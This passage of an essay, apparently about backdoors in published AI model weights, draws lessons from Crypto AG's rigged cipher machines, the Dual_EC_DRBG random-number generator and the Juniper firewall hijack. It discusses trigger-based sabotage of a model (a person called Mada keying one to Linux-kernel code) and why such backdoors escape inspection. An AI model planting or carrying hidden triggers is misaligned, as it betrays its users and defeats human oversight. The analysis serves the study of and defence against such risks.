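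Crypto AG made secure cipher machines for friendly governments and weakened ones for the rest. A cipher machine scrambles a message with a long stream of characters that should look random to anyone without the key. The weakened machines produced streams with hidden regularities, which let the NSA break messages in seconds that might otherwise have taken months. In the 1980s, these machines accounted for about 40% of the foreign government messages that the NSA decoded. A digital signature from Crypto AG would have passed every check, because the machines really did come from the company.

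Some of the company's own engineers noticed the weaknesses. In 1977 it fired one who had fixed them in Syria's machines. Another, Mengia Caflisch, designed a cipher so strong that the NSA feared it couldn't read the messages, and the factory put the cipher in 50 machines before managers stopped it. Sabotaging a model might involve far fewer people. Mada did it alone, and colleagues who later worked on the model would have no faulty formula to find.

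Customers became suspicious too, but most did little about it. Argentina challenged Crypto AG after losing the Falklands War in 1982. The company sent an expert to Buenos Aires, who blamed an old voice scrambler and said Argentina's main machines were unbreakable, and Argentina kept buying. In 1992 Iran arrested a salesman, Hans Bühler, who knew nothing of the secret, and held him for nine months. When he later told reporters about his suspicions, several countries suspended or cancelled contracts, but Iran did not.

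The Crypto AG case weakens the argument that fear of discovery will keep publishers honest. The company's owners wanted intelligence more than sales, and the business survived decades of suspicion because no outsider could prove anything. The case also weakens the argument for choosing suppliers by country, since many customers chose Crypto AG partly because it was Swiss.

A publisher that posts a single file for everyone can't give one country a good version and another a bad one, as a seller of machines can. To target one victim, it would need a trigger that recognizes that victim, such as Mada's Linux-kernel code, and every researcher would have a copy of the file to examine. Crypto AG's customers had to find the flaw in machines that they kept secret from each other.

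### Dual_EC_DRBG

In 2006 NIST published a standard for random number generators. One of the four it recommended was Dual_EC_DRBG, which the NSA had promoted. It uses two fixed points, $P$ and $Q$, on an elliptic curve. Multiplying such a point by a number is easy, but finding the number from the result is infeasible. The generator has a secret state $s_i$, and at each step it computes

$$r_i = x(s_iQ), \qquad s_{i+1} = x(s_iP),$$

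where $x$ means the first coordinate of a point. It outputs $r_i$ without its first 16 bits and uses $s_{i+1}$ as its next state.

The standard gave values for $P$ and $Q$ but didn't explain how anyone had chosen $Q$. In 2007 Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson of Microsoft showed why this mattered. Whoever chose the points could have done so in a way that gave them a secret number $d$ with $P = dQ$. Then

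$$d\,(s_iQ) = s_i\,(dQ) = s_iP.$$

An eavesdropper who knows $d$ and sees one output can try all 65,536 values of the missing bits to recover $s_iQ$, then multiply it by $d$ to get the next state. They can then predict everything the generator produces, including secret keys. Programs often send some random numbers unencrypted when they set up a secure connection, so an eavesdropper could get the output they need.

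Shumow and Ferguson could prove that a backdoor was possible but not that anyone held $d$. The generator stayed in the standard for years. In 2013 news organizations reported, citing documents leaked by Edward Snowden, that the NSA had deliberately weakened it, and NIST told people to stop using it. Reuters reported that the NSA had paid the security company RSA $10 million to make the generator the default in one of its products. RSA denied knowingly weakening anything. Nobody has published $d$, but few cryptographers now doubt that the backdoor was deliberate.

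Outsiders warned about the problem within about a year because the standard was a page of mathematics that anyone could read. They couldn't have found it by testing, since the output looks normal to anyone without $d$. The remedy was also simple, because a designer can derive $Q$ by a public procedure that prevents them from choosing a secret $d$. A model's weights, by contrast, depend on training data and many other choices, and checking the random seed covers only one of them.

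An intruder later took over the same kind of backdoor at Juniper Networks, which used Dual_EC_DRBG in its firewalls with its own value of $Q$. In 2012 the intruder replaced that value in Juniper's source code, and Juniper unknowingly shipped the altered software to customers until it discovered the change in 2015. Anyone who knew the $d$ for the new $Q$ could decrypt traffic that customers believed was private.

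The intruder who took over the Juniper backdoor had to get inside the company and change the product. Most of the backdoors researchers have put in models would be easier to take over, because they have no secret key and anyone who learns the trigger can use it. Juniper could also send its customers a corrected version, but a model's publisher often doesn't know who has its weights.
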